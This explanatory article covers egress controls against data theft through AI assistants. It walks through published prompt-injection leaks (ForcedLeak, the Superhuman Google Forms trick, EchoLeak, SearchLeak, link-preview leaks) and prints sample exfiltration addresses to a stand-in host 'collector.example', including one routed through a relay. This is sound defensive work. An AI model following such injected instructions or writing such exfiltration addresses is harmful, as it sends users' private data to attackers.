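# Egress controls for AI assistants: checking outgoing email, web requests and links to stop data theft

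## How data can leave through an AI assistant, and where code can check it

Egress controls are ordinary code that inspects what an AI assistant sends out, then allows it, blocks it or asks the user. Network engineers use "egress" for traffic leaving a network, and companies were checking theirs for leaks long before AI assistants existed. Assistants made this harder because many of them read a user's mail, files and calendar in the same session as web pages and messages from strangers. A stranger can plant text in those pages or messages that leads the assistant to send private data to an outsider in an email, a web request or the address of an image. Security specialists call such a leak exfiltration.

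### From text to action

Every such assistant is built around a large language model, which takes in text and produces more text. The model cannot open a file or reach the internet on its own, so a conventional program called the controller does those things. *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026) describes the usual arrangement, in which the controller builds the model's input, or context, from the user's prompts, the conversation so far, earlier tool calls and their results.

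Model output takes effect in two ways, the first of which is the tool call. The developer gives the model a list of available functions, such as "fetch a page" or "send a message", and the model writes a short structured text that names a function and gives its input values. The controller detects this text, runs the function and adds the result to the context, and the model continues. A long task can repeat this loop dozens of times before the user gets an answer.

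Data can also leave through the answer itself. Models write with simple formatting marks, which the application turns into a page with headings, links and pictures. If the answer contains the address of a picture, the user's browser immediately requests the picture from the server at that address, even though the model hasn't called a tool and the user hasn't clicked anything.

### Instructions from strangers

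In indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content the assistant reads, such as an email or web page, and the model follows them. The attacker never types anything into the assistant. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter whose system asks a model to score each CV against the job requirements. A candidate hides text in the CV telling the model to approve it, and the model treats that text as an instruction instead of as part of the CV it is scoring.

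SQL injection looks like the same problem. An attacker types a database command into a web form, and the database runs it. Programmers prevent this by sending the command and the form's values separately, so the database never treats a value as a command. David C argues that no equivalent fix is possible in language models. A model receives one sequence of tokens (words and fragments of words) and predicts the next one, and nothing in that operation separates instructions from data.

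Developers label parts of the sequence as the user's text or a tool's output, and they train models to respect the labels. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) rates labels and written warnings as useful engineering but not as a hard security boundary. To find out why, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, wrapped identical passages of web text in different labels and trained small classifiers to identify the label from the model's internal activity. Because the passages were identical, the classifiers could learn only the trace left by the label. But when the researchers tested text whose style and label disagreed, the classifiers' output followed the style, so text written the way users write was classified as a user's even when it was labeled as tool output. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak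 data, the success rate rose from 2% where this confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) also proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible for models that represent instructions and data in the same vector space without an enforced separation. The failure rate can still be low, as it is in newer models. Attacks on Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 succeeded in none of 129 browser scenarios and in 2.0% of cases after 15 attempts on a broader test, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*. But *FrontierBreach*, the security vendor PromptArmor's own benchmark, still records successful attacks on leading models from every provider. Even a small failure rate matters, because anyone can write to a mailbox and sending a thousand variants of a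 message costs almost nothing.

### The lethal trifecta

A prompt injection can leak data only under certain conditions. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Simon Willison (2025), the software developer who named prompt injection in 2022, lists three: the assistant has access to private data, it takes in untrusted content, and it can communicate externally. Without private data there is nothing worth stealing, without untrusted content the attacker has no way to give the assistant instructions, and without external communication the data can't leave.

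Of the three elements, private data, untrusted content and an exit, Willison (2026) calls the exit "by far the easiest leg to restrict" without making the system much less useful. Private data is usually the point of the product, since an assistant that cannot read the user's mail cannot sort it. Untrusted content is nearly as hard to exclude, because email and the web consist largely of things other people wrote. Willison lists seventeen reported leaks in products from OpenAI, Google, Microsoft, Slack and others between April 2023 and June 2025, and writes that the vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the exit the data had taken.

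Blocking the ways out may be the easiest defence, but it is still not easy. Willison also describes the ways a tool might pass data out as "almost limitless", and closing them thoroughly means giving up useful features. For example, OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting, limits browsing to stored copies of pages so that no live request leaves the company's own network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. The help page, *Lockdown Mode*, adds that the setting switches off deep research and agent mode, and that ChatGPT may no longer show images from the web. OpenAI recommends the setting for people who handle sensitive data and says it is not for everyone.

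David C's article describes another way to break up the combination, which it credits to an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista. While a model processes text from some party, its privileges drop to that party's level, so an assistant reading a stranger's email would lose access to privileged tools. The rule is simple, but it would block much of what people want from an email assistant, which is to read a stranger's message and then act on it using the user's own calendar and files. Most products have kept the combination and check outgoing data instead.

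### How an address carries a secret

Much outgoing data travels inside web addresses, which have more room in them than they appear to. Consider this one, leaving off the opening "https://":

`pictures.example/cats/logo.png?size=large`

The part before the first slash, `pictures.example`, is the host, which determines which server gets the request. The path, `/cats/logo.png`, comes next and normally identifies a file or page on that server. Everything after the question mark is the query string, a list of names and values. Here it contains a single value for the size.

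Only the host has to be real. The browser uses it to find the server, then sends the path and query string unchanged. The server's owner decides how to handle them, so no file called `logo.png` needs to exist. Web servers also commonly log every requested address. The path and query string can therefore carry arbitrary text to whoever runs the host.

Suppose a user's calendar contains the code name of a surprise party, "marmalade", and an attacker who owns `collector.example` wants it. An injected instruction has already taken hold of the assistant. The word could now leave in any of these ways:

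- **In an image address.** The answer includes a picture at `collector.example/dot.png?w=marmalade`. The user's browser requests it, the word lands in the attacker's log, and the server sends back a transparent dot.
- **In a fetched page.** The assistant calls its page-fetching tool with `collector.example/marmalade`. This request starts from the vendor's servers instead of the user's browser. The page may not exist, but an error message in reply makes no difference, because the word went out with the question.
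- **In an email.** The assistant calls its mail tool with the attacker as recipient and puts the word in the subject, the body or an attachment.

The image is the hardest for the user to notice. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that such requests can happen in the background, and that data can leak even if the model writes nothing sensitive in the chat. An attack is called zero-click if it needs no action from the victim beyond normal use of the assistant.

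### Four places to check

Code can check outgoing data when the answer is displayed, when a tool is called, at the network proxy and at the mail gateway. These points differ mainly in how much information is available to the check.

The display code has the complete answer in readable form, including every link and image address. It can leave out images, show links as plain text, or block any host that isn't on an allowlist, a list of permitted destinations. The browser can also enforce a list if the page comes with a Content Security Policy, a header naming the hosts from which the page may load images and other resources. Checks at this stage come too late to stop requests that tools made while the model was working on the answer. They also don't apply outside the application. If someone posts the answer in a messaging app, that app may request the link itself to show a preview.

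Code can inspect a tool call before the controller carries it out, and it has more information there than at any other point. The values are unencrypted and separated by type, so the code can tell which one is the recipient. The controller also holds the whole conversation, so a rule can depend on where an address came from, such as whether the user typed it or it first appeared in a stranger's web page. Later checks can't apply this kind of provenance rule because they lack the conversation history.

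A tool-call check is weak when the call does not show what it will do. An agent that writes software can run commands, and the text of a command may not show what network traffic it will produce. Willison gives the example of a software package whose instructions tell the agent to run a helper program before testing. The helper is malicious and uploads every file it can find, but the command that starts it looks like routine setup and contains no address.

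A network proxy would catch that upload. It is a server through which an operator routes a machine's web traffic, and the machine is often the sealed-off environment in which an agent runs code. The proxy handles every request, regardless of which program made it. For an ordinary encrypted connection, it can detect the host name and the amount of data but cannot read the path, query string or body of the request. To let the proxy decrypt the traffic, an operator can install a certificate on the machine. This exposes everything in the request to the proxy, including passwords, and some programs will refuse to connect through it. Even with decryption, the proxy has no record of the conversation, so it cannot tell whether "marmalade" refers to the party or the recipe.

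The proxy also covers only the machines behind it. In the example, the user's browser sends the image request, perhaps from a home network, so the request does not pass through a proxy that filters traffic from the vendor's servers. DNS lookups, which turn host names into numeric addresses, can also bypass a web proxy unless the operator blocks them separately.

Outgoing mail can be checked at the mail gateway, a server that passes an organization's messages to the outside world. Gateway software can read the sender, all recipients including blind copies, the text and the attachments, unless the sender encrypted the message so that only the recipient can read it. Companies already use gateways to stop employees from mailing out customer lists. The gateway usually cannot determine whether a person or an assistant wrote the message, or whether the recipient's address came from the user's contacts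 or from a stranger's email. Internal mail may not pass through the gateway, but it can still leak data, because a message to the user's own inbox can contain a picture, and opening the message then sends a web request to the picture's host.

### Where it goes and what it carries

At any of the four points, a rule can check where data is going or what it contains. A destination check limits which hosts, exact web addresses or email recipients data may be sent to. A content filter limits what an outgoing message may carry, based on its text, patterns or statistics. It might look for sixteen-digit numbers in the format of payment card numbers, or for long, random-looking strings like the passwords programs use to access each other.

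The party example shows that destination checks and content filters fail in different ways. A destination check stops the leak because `collector.example` is not on the list, so it does not need to identify "marmalade" as private. But it can miss leaks through hosts that are on the list. OpenAI notes that many legitimate sites support redirects, so a request can begin at a trusted host and end at an attacker's. Other permitted services will store or forward data for anyone who signs up, including attackers. A content filter does not depend on whether the host is trustworthy, but it has to recognize the secret, and "marmalade" is a dictionary word that matches no pattern. Even if the word is on the filter's list of forbidden words, the model can get it past the filter by spelling it backwards.

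Rules about destination and rules about content overlap in a web address, because the path and query string are part of the destination and can also carry data. If a rule approves only the host, the sender can put anything in the rest of the address. A rule that approves only exact full addresses prevents this, which is why OpenAI switched to one. Some information can still leak through the choice of which approved address to request, but far less per request.

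After the check, the code has to allow the request, block it or ask the user. Allowing and blocking are simple to carry out, but either can be a mistake. Blocking a harmless request breaks the user's task, and users who run into this often will try to turn the check off. Asking the user seems to avoid having to choose between allowing and blocking. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a mechanism in ChatGPT for transmissions that look risky. It either shows the user the information about to be sent and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way.

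People are poor at judging confirmation requests. OpenAI warns that frequent alerts lead users to click through without thinking. In an Anthropic study that Willison reported in August 2026, 1,053 paid testers worked with a coding agent that asked permission for its actions. Partway through each session, the experimenters replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The study used computer commands rather than outgoing messages, and Anthropic was making the case for its own automatic checker. Still, the result leaves little reason to rely on a confirmation box alone. A box that shows the actual data and recipient gives the user more to judge by than a bare request for permission, but the study did not test whether this improves decisions.

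### Damage control

OpenAI compares the assistant to a customer-service employee who can give refunds. Some callers will lie successfully, so the company trains its staff and also has the computer cap the refund. In security engineering terms, an attacker needs a source (a way to influence the system) and a sink (a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context). An egress control limits what the sink can do, like the cap on refunds.

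*Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) distinguishes between an injection being present in the input and an attack succeeding. A detector that looks for injections has to recognize hostile text, which an attacker can reword endlessly. A destination check avoids this, the hardest part of the problem, by comparing an address with a list. It gives the same result every time, however the text is worded. Willison praises Lockdown Mode because its mechanisms are deterministic, whereas an AI system acting as the judge would itself be open to manipulation.

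The injection, however, remains in the context and keeps influencing the model. OpenAI states that under Lockdown Mode a malicious instruction in an uploaded file can still cause a wrong answer. It also does not promise that exfiltration is impossible, since risk remains through connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features and undiscovered techniques. Other harms don't require the assistant to send anything, so egress controls cannot stop them. For example, hidden text in an invoice can lead the assistant to report the wrong account number, and the user then makes the payment to that account.

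## Images and link previews: the first fixes and the allowlists that failed

Most of the early data leaks from AI assistants happened through images in their answers. Vendors tried several fixes, and many settled on an allowlist of hosts from which images could load. In 2025, researchers got private data past the allowlists at Salesforce and the email company Superhuman.

### From a line of text to a web request

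The formatting marks in a chat answer usually follow a convention called Markdown. A picture consists of an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and an address in parentheses:

`![A cat](https://pictures.example/cats/logo.png?size=large)`

This line becomes a web request in four steps:

1. The model writes the line as part of its answer. At this point it is only text.
2. The application's display code recognizes the marks and converts the line to HTML, the language of web pages. The result is an image element with the same address as its source.
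3. The browser adds the element to the page and immediately requests `/cats/logo.png?size=large` from `pictures.example`.
4. The server logs the request and returns a picture, which the browser draws.

These automatic requests are rarely a problem on an ordinary web page, because the page's author chose the addresses. In a chat application, the model writes the addresses, so a prompt injection can control where the requests go.

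### The first reports

According to Willison's *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, Roman Samoilenko described this leak for ChatGPT in April 2023. Samoilenko's version depended on the user copying text from a rigged web page and pasting it into the chat. The page added hidden instructions to the copied text.

The security researcher Johann Rehberger found a version of the attack that needed no pasting. Microsoft's Bing Chat could read the web page a user had open, so instructions on the page reached the model. In the demonstration described in *Bing Chat*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, the test page held the instructions and, further down, a secret. Rehberger had the assistant wait two turns before writing the image, to show how much control the injected text had over the conversation. The image's address then carried a short encoded summary of the page and the chat, including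 the secret, to Rehberger's server. An attacker would not need to own the page, since a comment or an advertisement on it could hold the instructions.

Rehberger reported the flaw on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft told him on June 15 that it had been fixed. The old tests no longer worked, and Bing Chat now had a Content Security Policy that allowed images from four Bing hosts. Rehberger did not know the full details of the fix but thought the policy was at least part of it.

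Anthropic fixed Claude differently. In that case, hostile text in the middle of an uploaded biography of Albert Einstein led Claude to put a summary of the user's earlier messages into an image address. Rehberger reported this on July 12, 2023, and Anthropic closed the report two weeks later. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Claude no longer loaded such images until the user clicked "Show Image". This stopped the automatic leak, but Rehberger considered it imperfect. A user who expects a picture has little reason not to click, and the click sends the same request as before.

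Microsoft made an even smaller change to its Azure AI Playground that September. As far as Rehberger could tell in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, the company inserted a space into the Markdown so that the display code no longer recognized an image. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, OpenAI had known about the problem in ChatGPT since early April 2023 but didn't check image addresses until December, and at first only in the web app.

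### How a Content Security Policy works

The policy that Bing Chat adopted is a general web standard, older than chat assistants. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web's main standards body, defines it as a set of directives, most of which name a type of resource and the places it may come from. The directive for images is `img-src`. A chat page might arrive with this header:

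`Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' pictures.example`

`'self'` stands for the site that served the page. Before the browser requests an image, it compares the address with the `img-src` list. If no entry matches, the browser reports a network error to the page and sends nothing. Under this policy, the browser would not request the image at `collector.example` that carried the word "marmalade". The browser applies the rule however the image got onto the page, so the policy still works if the display code has a bug. It checks again when a server redirects an image request, so a redirect from `pictures.example` to `collector.example` also fails.

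An entry on the list can name a single host, all subdomains of a domain (`*.pictures.example`), or a host and a path, but it cannot specify a query string. Even an entry for one particular file therefore lets the query string carry data. After a redirect, the browser also ignores the path and accepts any file on a listed host. W3C chose this rule because strict path matching would let a hostile page work out where other sites redirect their visitors.

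A policy also protects only as well as its least restrictive directive, according to the section on exfiltration in W3C's draft. For example, a policy that contains `img-src *` but forbids everything else still allows images from anywhere, so it doesn't prevent leaks. Leaving out `default-src`, the fallback for other resource types, is also risky because some requests, such as those a browser makes in advance to speed up loading, have no directive of their own.

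The policy does not cover clicked links. One of the draft's 22 directives limits where a form may send its contents, but none limits where an ordinary link may lead. An assistant can therefore show a link with private data in its address, and the data leaves if the user clicks it.

The policy also does not affect requests from servers, such as those made by a page-fetching tool, because only the browser enforces it. W3C recommends the policy as an extra layer of defence and advises against relying on it as the first.

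### Removing links, or trusting some hosts

Amazon went further in January 2024 with Amazon Q, its assistant for businesses. An injection had led Q to write a link with the chat history in its query string, and Amazon responded by preventing the assistant from showing links at all. This also prevents leaks through clicked links, which a Content Security Policy doesn't stop. It is a considerable drawback for an assistant that answers from company documents, because it can no longer link to the document it used. Microsoft lets customers decide in Copilot Studio, its tool for building agents. Microsoft's *Control image rendering and embedded URLs* explains that administrators can turn off images and clickable links to prevent data theft.

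Microsoft (for Bing Chat) and GitHub (for Copilot Chat, in 2024) allowed images only from trusted hosts, so their products could still show some pictures. This protection depends on every host on the list, and Willison recorded two failures before the end of 2023.

Google's Bard accepted images from any subdomain of `google.com`, including `script.google.com`, where Google's Apps Script service runs small programs for its users. An attacker could use one of these programs to collect the data. Writer.com, a writing assistant for companies, similarly allowed every subdomain of `cloudfront.net`, where Amazon gives addresses to customers of its content delivery service. Researchers reported the problem to Writer on November 29. The company replied that it did not consider this a security issue, but the leak appeared to be closed by December 18.

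In both products, the allowlist contained a trusted relay, a permitted service that will forward or store data for anyone. The browser enforced the list correctly, but the mistake was to treat a domain name as proof of who would read the data.

### Salesforce and the five-dollar domain

Companies keep customer records in Salesforce's software, and Agentforce adds AI agents that can read and act on those records. Many companies also use Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature, a web form where possible customers, or "leads", enter their contact details directly into the database. Anyone can fill it in.

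The security company Noma found that this was enough to steal data, and named the flaw ForcedLeak. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025), a forum repost of Noma's report, explains how the researchers looked for a field with room for instructions. The name, company and email fields held 40 to 80 characters each, but the description field held 42,000. An employee would later make a normal request, asking Agentforce to look at the new lead and answer its questions. The agent then also followed the instructions in the description, looked up the email addresses of other leads, and added a picture with those addresses in the query string of its URL.

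A Content Security Policy should have stopped the picture from loading. Noma found 22 host entries in the policy, including the subdomains of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired. Noma bought the domain for $5, and the browser sent the data to Noma's server because the policy allowed its address.

The list also included every subdomain of `amazonaws.com`, where Amazon's cloud customers run their own services. Noma did not need to use this weakness. But an attacker could probably have set up a service there to collect the data, so renewing the expired domain would not have been enough.

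Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025, and published its findings on September 25. In between, Salesforce took back the domain and, on September 8, began enforcing a mechanism called Trusted URLs for its agents. In a statement quoted by The Hacker News (2025), Salesforce described the mechanism as a defence for when an injection has already succeeded. In the same article, Itay Ravia of Aim Labs considered ForcedLeak a variant of EchoLeak, an earlier leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

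### What Trusted URLs changed

Trusted URLs checks addresses in the text of the answer instead of in the browser. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* describes how, in the Salesforce web app, code finds every address in an answer before it appears, including those inside HTML and style instructions, and replaces any that the company has not approved with a placeholder. This is stronger than an image rule alone because the browser never receives the unapproved address, so the browser cannot request it and the user cannot click it.

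Administrators have to approve each outside domain their agents use, and they choose which types of resource the browser may load from it. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* notes that they may use wildcards, and that an approved domain is permitted throughout the company's Salesforce system, not just for its agents. PromptArmor advises against permitting images from a domain unless the agent needs to show them, and against wildcards that cover sites where strangers can post content.

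Even a careful administrator controls only part of the browser's policy. According to *CspTrustedSite*, Salesforce's developer reference, the company adds its own addresses to each directive and updates them regularly, and these do not appear among the customer's entries. The expired domain carried Salesforce's name and was probably one of these addresses, in which case a customer reviewing its own list would not have found it.

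Trusted URLs also does not limit what an agent does with its tools. In April 2026, OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026) recorded another theft of data from Agentforce through a public form, in research by Capsule Security. The instructions again arrived in a lead, but the agent emailed out the customer records, according to a news report on longform.social. Removing untrusted addresses from the displayed answer does not stop the agent from sending an email.

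### Superhuman and the Google Form

Checking who owned each allowlisted domain would have exposed the problem in ForcedLeak, but it would not have helped Superhuman. Superhuman's email app allowed images from `docs.google.com`, and the check would have found nothing wrong because Google has owned that host throughout.

But Google also uses it for Google Forms, which lets anyone create a questionnaire and collect the answers. Web software normally uses different kinds of request to retrieve something and to submit data, and browsers load pictures with the retrieving kind, called GET. Google Forms also accepts answers through GET, so that the owner of a form can hand out links with the answers already filled in. A browser that loads such a link as a picture therefore submits the form.

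PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* shows how this defeated the allowlist. The attacker sends the victim an email with hidden instructions, which the victim does not need to open. When the user asks for a summary of recent mail, the assistant reads the instructions along with everything else from the last hour. It then writes an image address that points to the attacker's form, with the contents of the other emails in the query string. The browser sends the request because `docs.google.com` is on the allowlist. Google's reply is not an image, but the form has already stored the data. PromptArmor obtained the full text of several sensitive emails in a single answer, and parts of more than 40 in another test.

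Superhuman had approved the whole host. A narrower policy could have blocked the form, since an allowlist entry can include a path and forms have their own path on that host. The protection would still have been incomplete, because browsers ignore an entry's path after a redirect.

PromptArmor found two more leaks in the company's products, neither of which relied on Google. Superhuman Go, a newer assistant that reads web pages and connects to services such as Gmail, loaded a one-pixel image directly from the attacker's domain. In the email app, the assistant's web search feature could open any address, so an injection could make it open one on the attacker's server with private mail in the query string. The browser's image rules would not apply to that request.

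PromptArmor sent its first report on the evening of Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released the first patch the next day. It patched its other products on December 18 and released more patches on January 11, 2026, after further findings. PromptArmor praised the speed of the response but did not describe what the new code checks.

People who write allowlists still see the same host as harmless. Agentforce Coworker, a Salesforce product in beta, removes URLs by default, and *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* explains how administrators can approve the ones they need for outside data. Its example is `https://docs.google.com`. If an administrator approves that URL, a link to an attacker's form could remain in an answer for the user to click. Approval alone does not recreate Superhuman's flaw, because loading images requires a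 separate permission.

### New products, same flaw

By 2025 the image leak was well known but still appeared in new products. That November, a researcher reported it in Antigravity, Google's new programming tool, where an image could carry data to the attacker's own domain. Willison writes that Google classified the report as intended behavior.

OpenAI had dealt with image leaks in ChatGPT years before it extended Codex, its coding agent, to everyday tasks such as sorting email. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes an attack on this version much like the one on Superhuman. One hostile email led Codex to write an image whose address submitted the user's other emails to a Google Form. The user had only asked for help with the inbox. PromptArmor reported the flaw on April 21, 2026. The service that handles OpenAI's bug reports confirmed it on May 14, and OpenAI had fixed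 it by the time PromptArmor published a week later.

This was a new product from a company with direct experience of the problem, and the attack came three months after PromptArmor published the same trick with Google Forms. Each application has its own display code and its own list of allowed hosts, so developers who add images and email access to a new agent have to build the check again.

### Link previews

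Developers can control the code that displays an assistant's answers only in their own applications. Many people now talk to agents through Slack or Telegram. When someone posts a link there, the app automatically requests the page and shows a preview with its title, description and a small picture. The preview sends the same type of request as a click.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains how link previews turn a link that someone would have to click into a zero-click leak. An injection leads the agent to write a link to the attacker's server with private data in the query string. When the agent posts its answer, the messaging app requests the page to build the preview, and the data arrives in the attacker's log, possibly before the user has read the message. Images in an email can cause a similar request when the user opens it, as Willison reports of Microsoft's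 Copilot Cowork.

PromptArmor tested this in 2026 with OpenClaw, an agent that people run themselves and instruct through messaging apps, and found it exposed on Telegram with the default settings. The company also set up a website where people can test other combinations of agent and app. The site logs each preview request and the data sent with it. In PromptArmor's example, the log contained a name and an API key (a password that programs use to access a service).

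The usual defences cannot stop this because the request to the attacker's server comes from the messaging company's software, over a different network. A Content Security Policy applies to the developer's own web page, which the user is not looking at. A network proxy around the agent would carry only an ordinary connection to Telegram, which it must allow for the agent to work.

The direct fix is to turn off link previews. When an OpenClaw user adds `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the configuration file, PromptArmor's test site no longer receives the data. The link remains in the message, so clicking it would still leak the data. Code that removes unapproved addresses before the agent posts its answer, as Trusted URLs does inside Salesforce, would prevent leaks through both previews and clicks.

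Previews are easy to turn off, but someone who connects OpenClaw to Telegram has no obvious reason to look for the setting. PromptArmor says messaging companies should let developers control previews, preferably for individual chats or channels, and agent developers should use that control or pass the choice on to their users. Control by channel would let people keep previews for links they send each other and turn them off where an agent posts.

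## Microsoft 365 Copilot: EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot, the AI assistant in Microsoft's office software, answers questions using an employee's mail, files, calendar and chats. A stranger can add to that material by sending an email. Security researchers have published three sets of attacks that leak data from Copilot: EchoLeak in June 2025, SearchLeak in June 2026 and ReLeak in December 2026. Microsoft fixed the flaws before each publication, but all three sets include a leak through a permitted Microsoft host that fetches outside addresses for anyone.

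### How an unread email reaches the model

When an employee asks Copilot a question, software first searches the employee's mailbox, stored files, internal websites and Teams chats. It then adds the best matches to the model's context along with the question, which is called retrieval-augmented generation. An attacker's email can be one of the matches even if the employee has never opened it. The attacker doesn't need an account at the company or a click from the employee, but the employee has to ask a question that brings up the email.

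Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains how the research group Aim Labs improved those odds. Search software of this type often converts each passage of text into a list of numbers, with similar numbers for similar meanings, and returns the passages whose numbers are closest to the question's. A short email is close to only a few questions, so Aim Labs wrote a long email with sections on ordinary office matters, such as staff leave, and repeated the instructions in every section. Aim Labs did not know how Copilot's search worked, but the email came up for questions on various topics.

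### EchoLeak: three checks in a row

Three checks stood between that email and the attacker's server. They ran in this order:

1. Before retrieved text reached the model, a classifier examined it for prompt injections.
2. After the model wrote its answer, code removed links and images with outside addresses.
3. When the answer appeared on screen, the browser applied a Content Security Policy that allowed images only from listed hosts.

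The classifier failed because Aim Labs phrased the instructions as a request to the human recipient and never mentioned AI. Many legitimate business emails ask the reader to collect information, so this text did not look like an attack. Ravia adds that developers have few realistic examples for training such classifiers. Copilot also cites the documents behind an answer, and a citation of the email might have alerted the employee. But the email asked its reader not to mention it, and Copilot left it out.

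The second check missed a notation. Markdown allows an author to write an image's address in the same line as the image, as in the earlier examples, or to put a label there and give the address elsewhere:

`![A cat][photo]`

`[photo]: https://pictures.example/cats/logo.png`

Copilot's display code produced the same picture from either form, but the removal code detected only the first. Links have the same two forms and had the same gap, so Aim Labs could already show the employee a link with private data in its address, and using an image instead meant the employee didn't have to click.

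This kind of gap can arise whenever two programs interpret the same text separately. Adding the missing notation to the removal code fixes one instance, but Ravia lists several other variants that got through. Checking after the conversion to HTML is more reliable, because by then every notation has become an image element with one source address.

The browser then blocked the image because the attacker's host was not on Copilot's list. Ravia's copy of the list has 29 different entries, mostly for Microsoft's own services, and 11 of them are wildcards that cover every subdomain. Aim Labs could make the browser request any address on those hosts, but it could not run a program there or read the reply, so it needed a service that would pass the data on by itself.

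SharePoint, Microsoft's software for internal websites, had a service that fetched outside material to embed in a page. The attack worked through this service only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. Aim Labs then found a Teams service that fetches a web address to prepare a preview. It required no invitation, so the leak became zero-click.

### Why the browser could not stop the second request

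Suppose a permitted host called `preview.example` runs such a service, and the model writes an image with this address:

`preview.example/fetch?url=collector.example/marmalade`

The browser finds `preview.example` on the list and sends the request. The server at `preview.example` reads the query string and requests `collector.example/marmalade` from its own network, which puts the secret word in the attacker's log.

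The Content Security Policy cannot block the second request, because only the browser enforces the policy and the browser does not send that request. In the first request, the attacker's host appears only in the query string, which the policy ignores.

A redirect would have failed because the browser would also have checked the new address, whereas a fetching service makes the request itself.

These services are trusted relays, like Google Forms in the attack on Superhuman, but the attacker does not need an account with them. Web security engineers call the weakness server-side request forgery. Many standard precautions address their usual worry, that an outsider will use the server to reach machines inside a private network. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), for example, recommends blocking private network addresses and long chains of redirects. Neither measure would have stopped this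 leak, because the attacker's server was an ordinary public one.

### After EchoLeak

Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft began partial repairs in the spring, installed the full fix on its own servers in May and published an advisory on June 11, the day Aim Labs released its findings. Abdullahi reported in *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit* that Microsoft assigned the flaw the identifier CVE-2025-32711, rated it critical and scored it 9.3 out of 10. Customers did not have to install anything, and Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed none were affected.

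Willison (2025) regarded EchoLeak as an extended variant of a leak already seen in a dozen products. It did send private data out in the same way, inside a web address. Ravia's claim that it was new depends on how the attack reached the assistant. Earlier demonstrations usually required the user to direct the assistant to a hostile page or file, or limited what the attacker could take, whereas EchoLeak needed only ordinary use and could leak anything in the model's context.

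Ravia also argued that the central fault came before any link or image, when an outsider's email influenced what Copilot did with the company's internal data. Ravia calls this an "LLM scope violation". Reddy and Gujral propose a provenance rule under which Copilot would answer from internal sources by default and include outside mail only when the user asks for it. This rule might have stopped EchoLeak at the first step, but Copilot would also have ignored relevant messages from customers and suppliers.

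Microsoft reportedly made narrower changes. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it, and that customers gained options to restrict external communication. This removes links already in the content, but the model can also write a link from a plain-language description, so its answer still needs to be checked.

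The same paper estimates which of eight defences would have stopped the automatic leak. Reddy and Gujral expect that a list of permitted addresses, a strict Content Security Policy, an image proxy with signed addresses, or human approval would have stopped it. They expect that labels on outside text and monitoring for private data would have failed. These are judgments, since they worked from public reports and ran no experiments. Copilot already had a Content Security Policy, so the estimate for that defence depends heavily on how strict the policy is. They advise listing only hosts that the application needs and avoiding wildcards.

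### SearchLeak: the sanitizer that ran too late

A year later, the security company Varonis found another attack, described in *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026). It targeted Copilot Enterprise Search, a version of Copilot for finding company mail, meetings and files. The attack began with a link to the search page on a genuine Microsoft domain. The page took its search text from the link's query string, and Copilot treated that text as instructions, so clicking the link started the attack without the user typing anything.

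The attacker's instructions arrived where the user's own prompt normally goes, so the attack did not need an email from a stranger to enter the context. A rule that classifies user input as trusted and retrieved documents as untrusted would have classified these instructions as trusted.

Copilot did have a safeguard against HTML in its answers. Code wrapped the finished answer in a block that told the browser to display any HTML as plain text, so an image element would appear as harmless characters. But Copilot showed the answer while the model was still writing it. The events came in this order:

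1. The model wrote an image element partway through its answer.
2. The browser added the element to the page and requested the image.
3. The model finished its answer.
4. The safeguard turned the image element into plain text.

Each component did what its programmers intended, but the safeguard could work only if the answer had no effect until it was complete. This is a race condition, a fault in which the result depends on which of two processes finishes first. After step 4 the picture was gone from the page, and the user saw only a slightly odd answer.

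### Checking an answer while it streams

A model can take many seconds to write a long answer, so most assistants stream it, displaying each piece as it arrives. A developer can avoid the race by holding back the whole answer until the check is done, but then the user waits in front of an empty screen.

Checking each piece separately does not work well either, because a piece can end anywhere. The name of a forbidden host might arrive as `collec` and then `tor.example`, and neither half matches a rule. The code has to keep earlier pieces. When an image or link begins, the code can hold back the text until the address is complete, check the whole address, and then display or discard the element. Ordinary sentences can still appear immediately.

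Taler recommends sanitizing "at render time", when the application turns text into page elements. If the code that creates an image always checks the address first, the browser cannot request an unapproved address, no matter how early it appears in the answer. This check would also have worked for the notation that EchoLeak used, in which the address may come many lines after the image. The application cannot create the image until it has the address, so it can check the address then.

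### Bing as the relay

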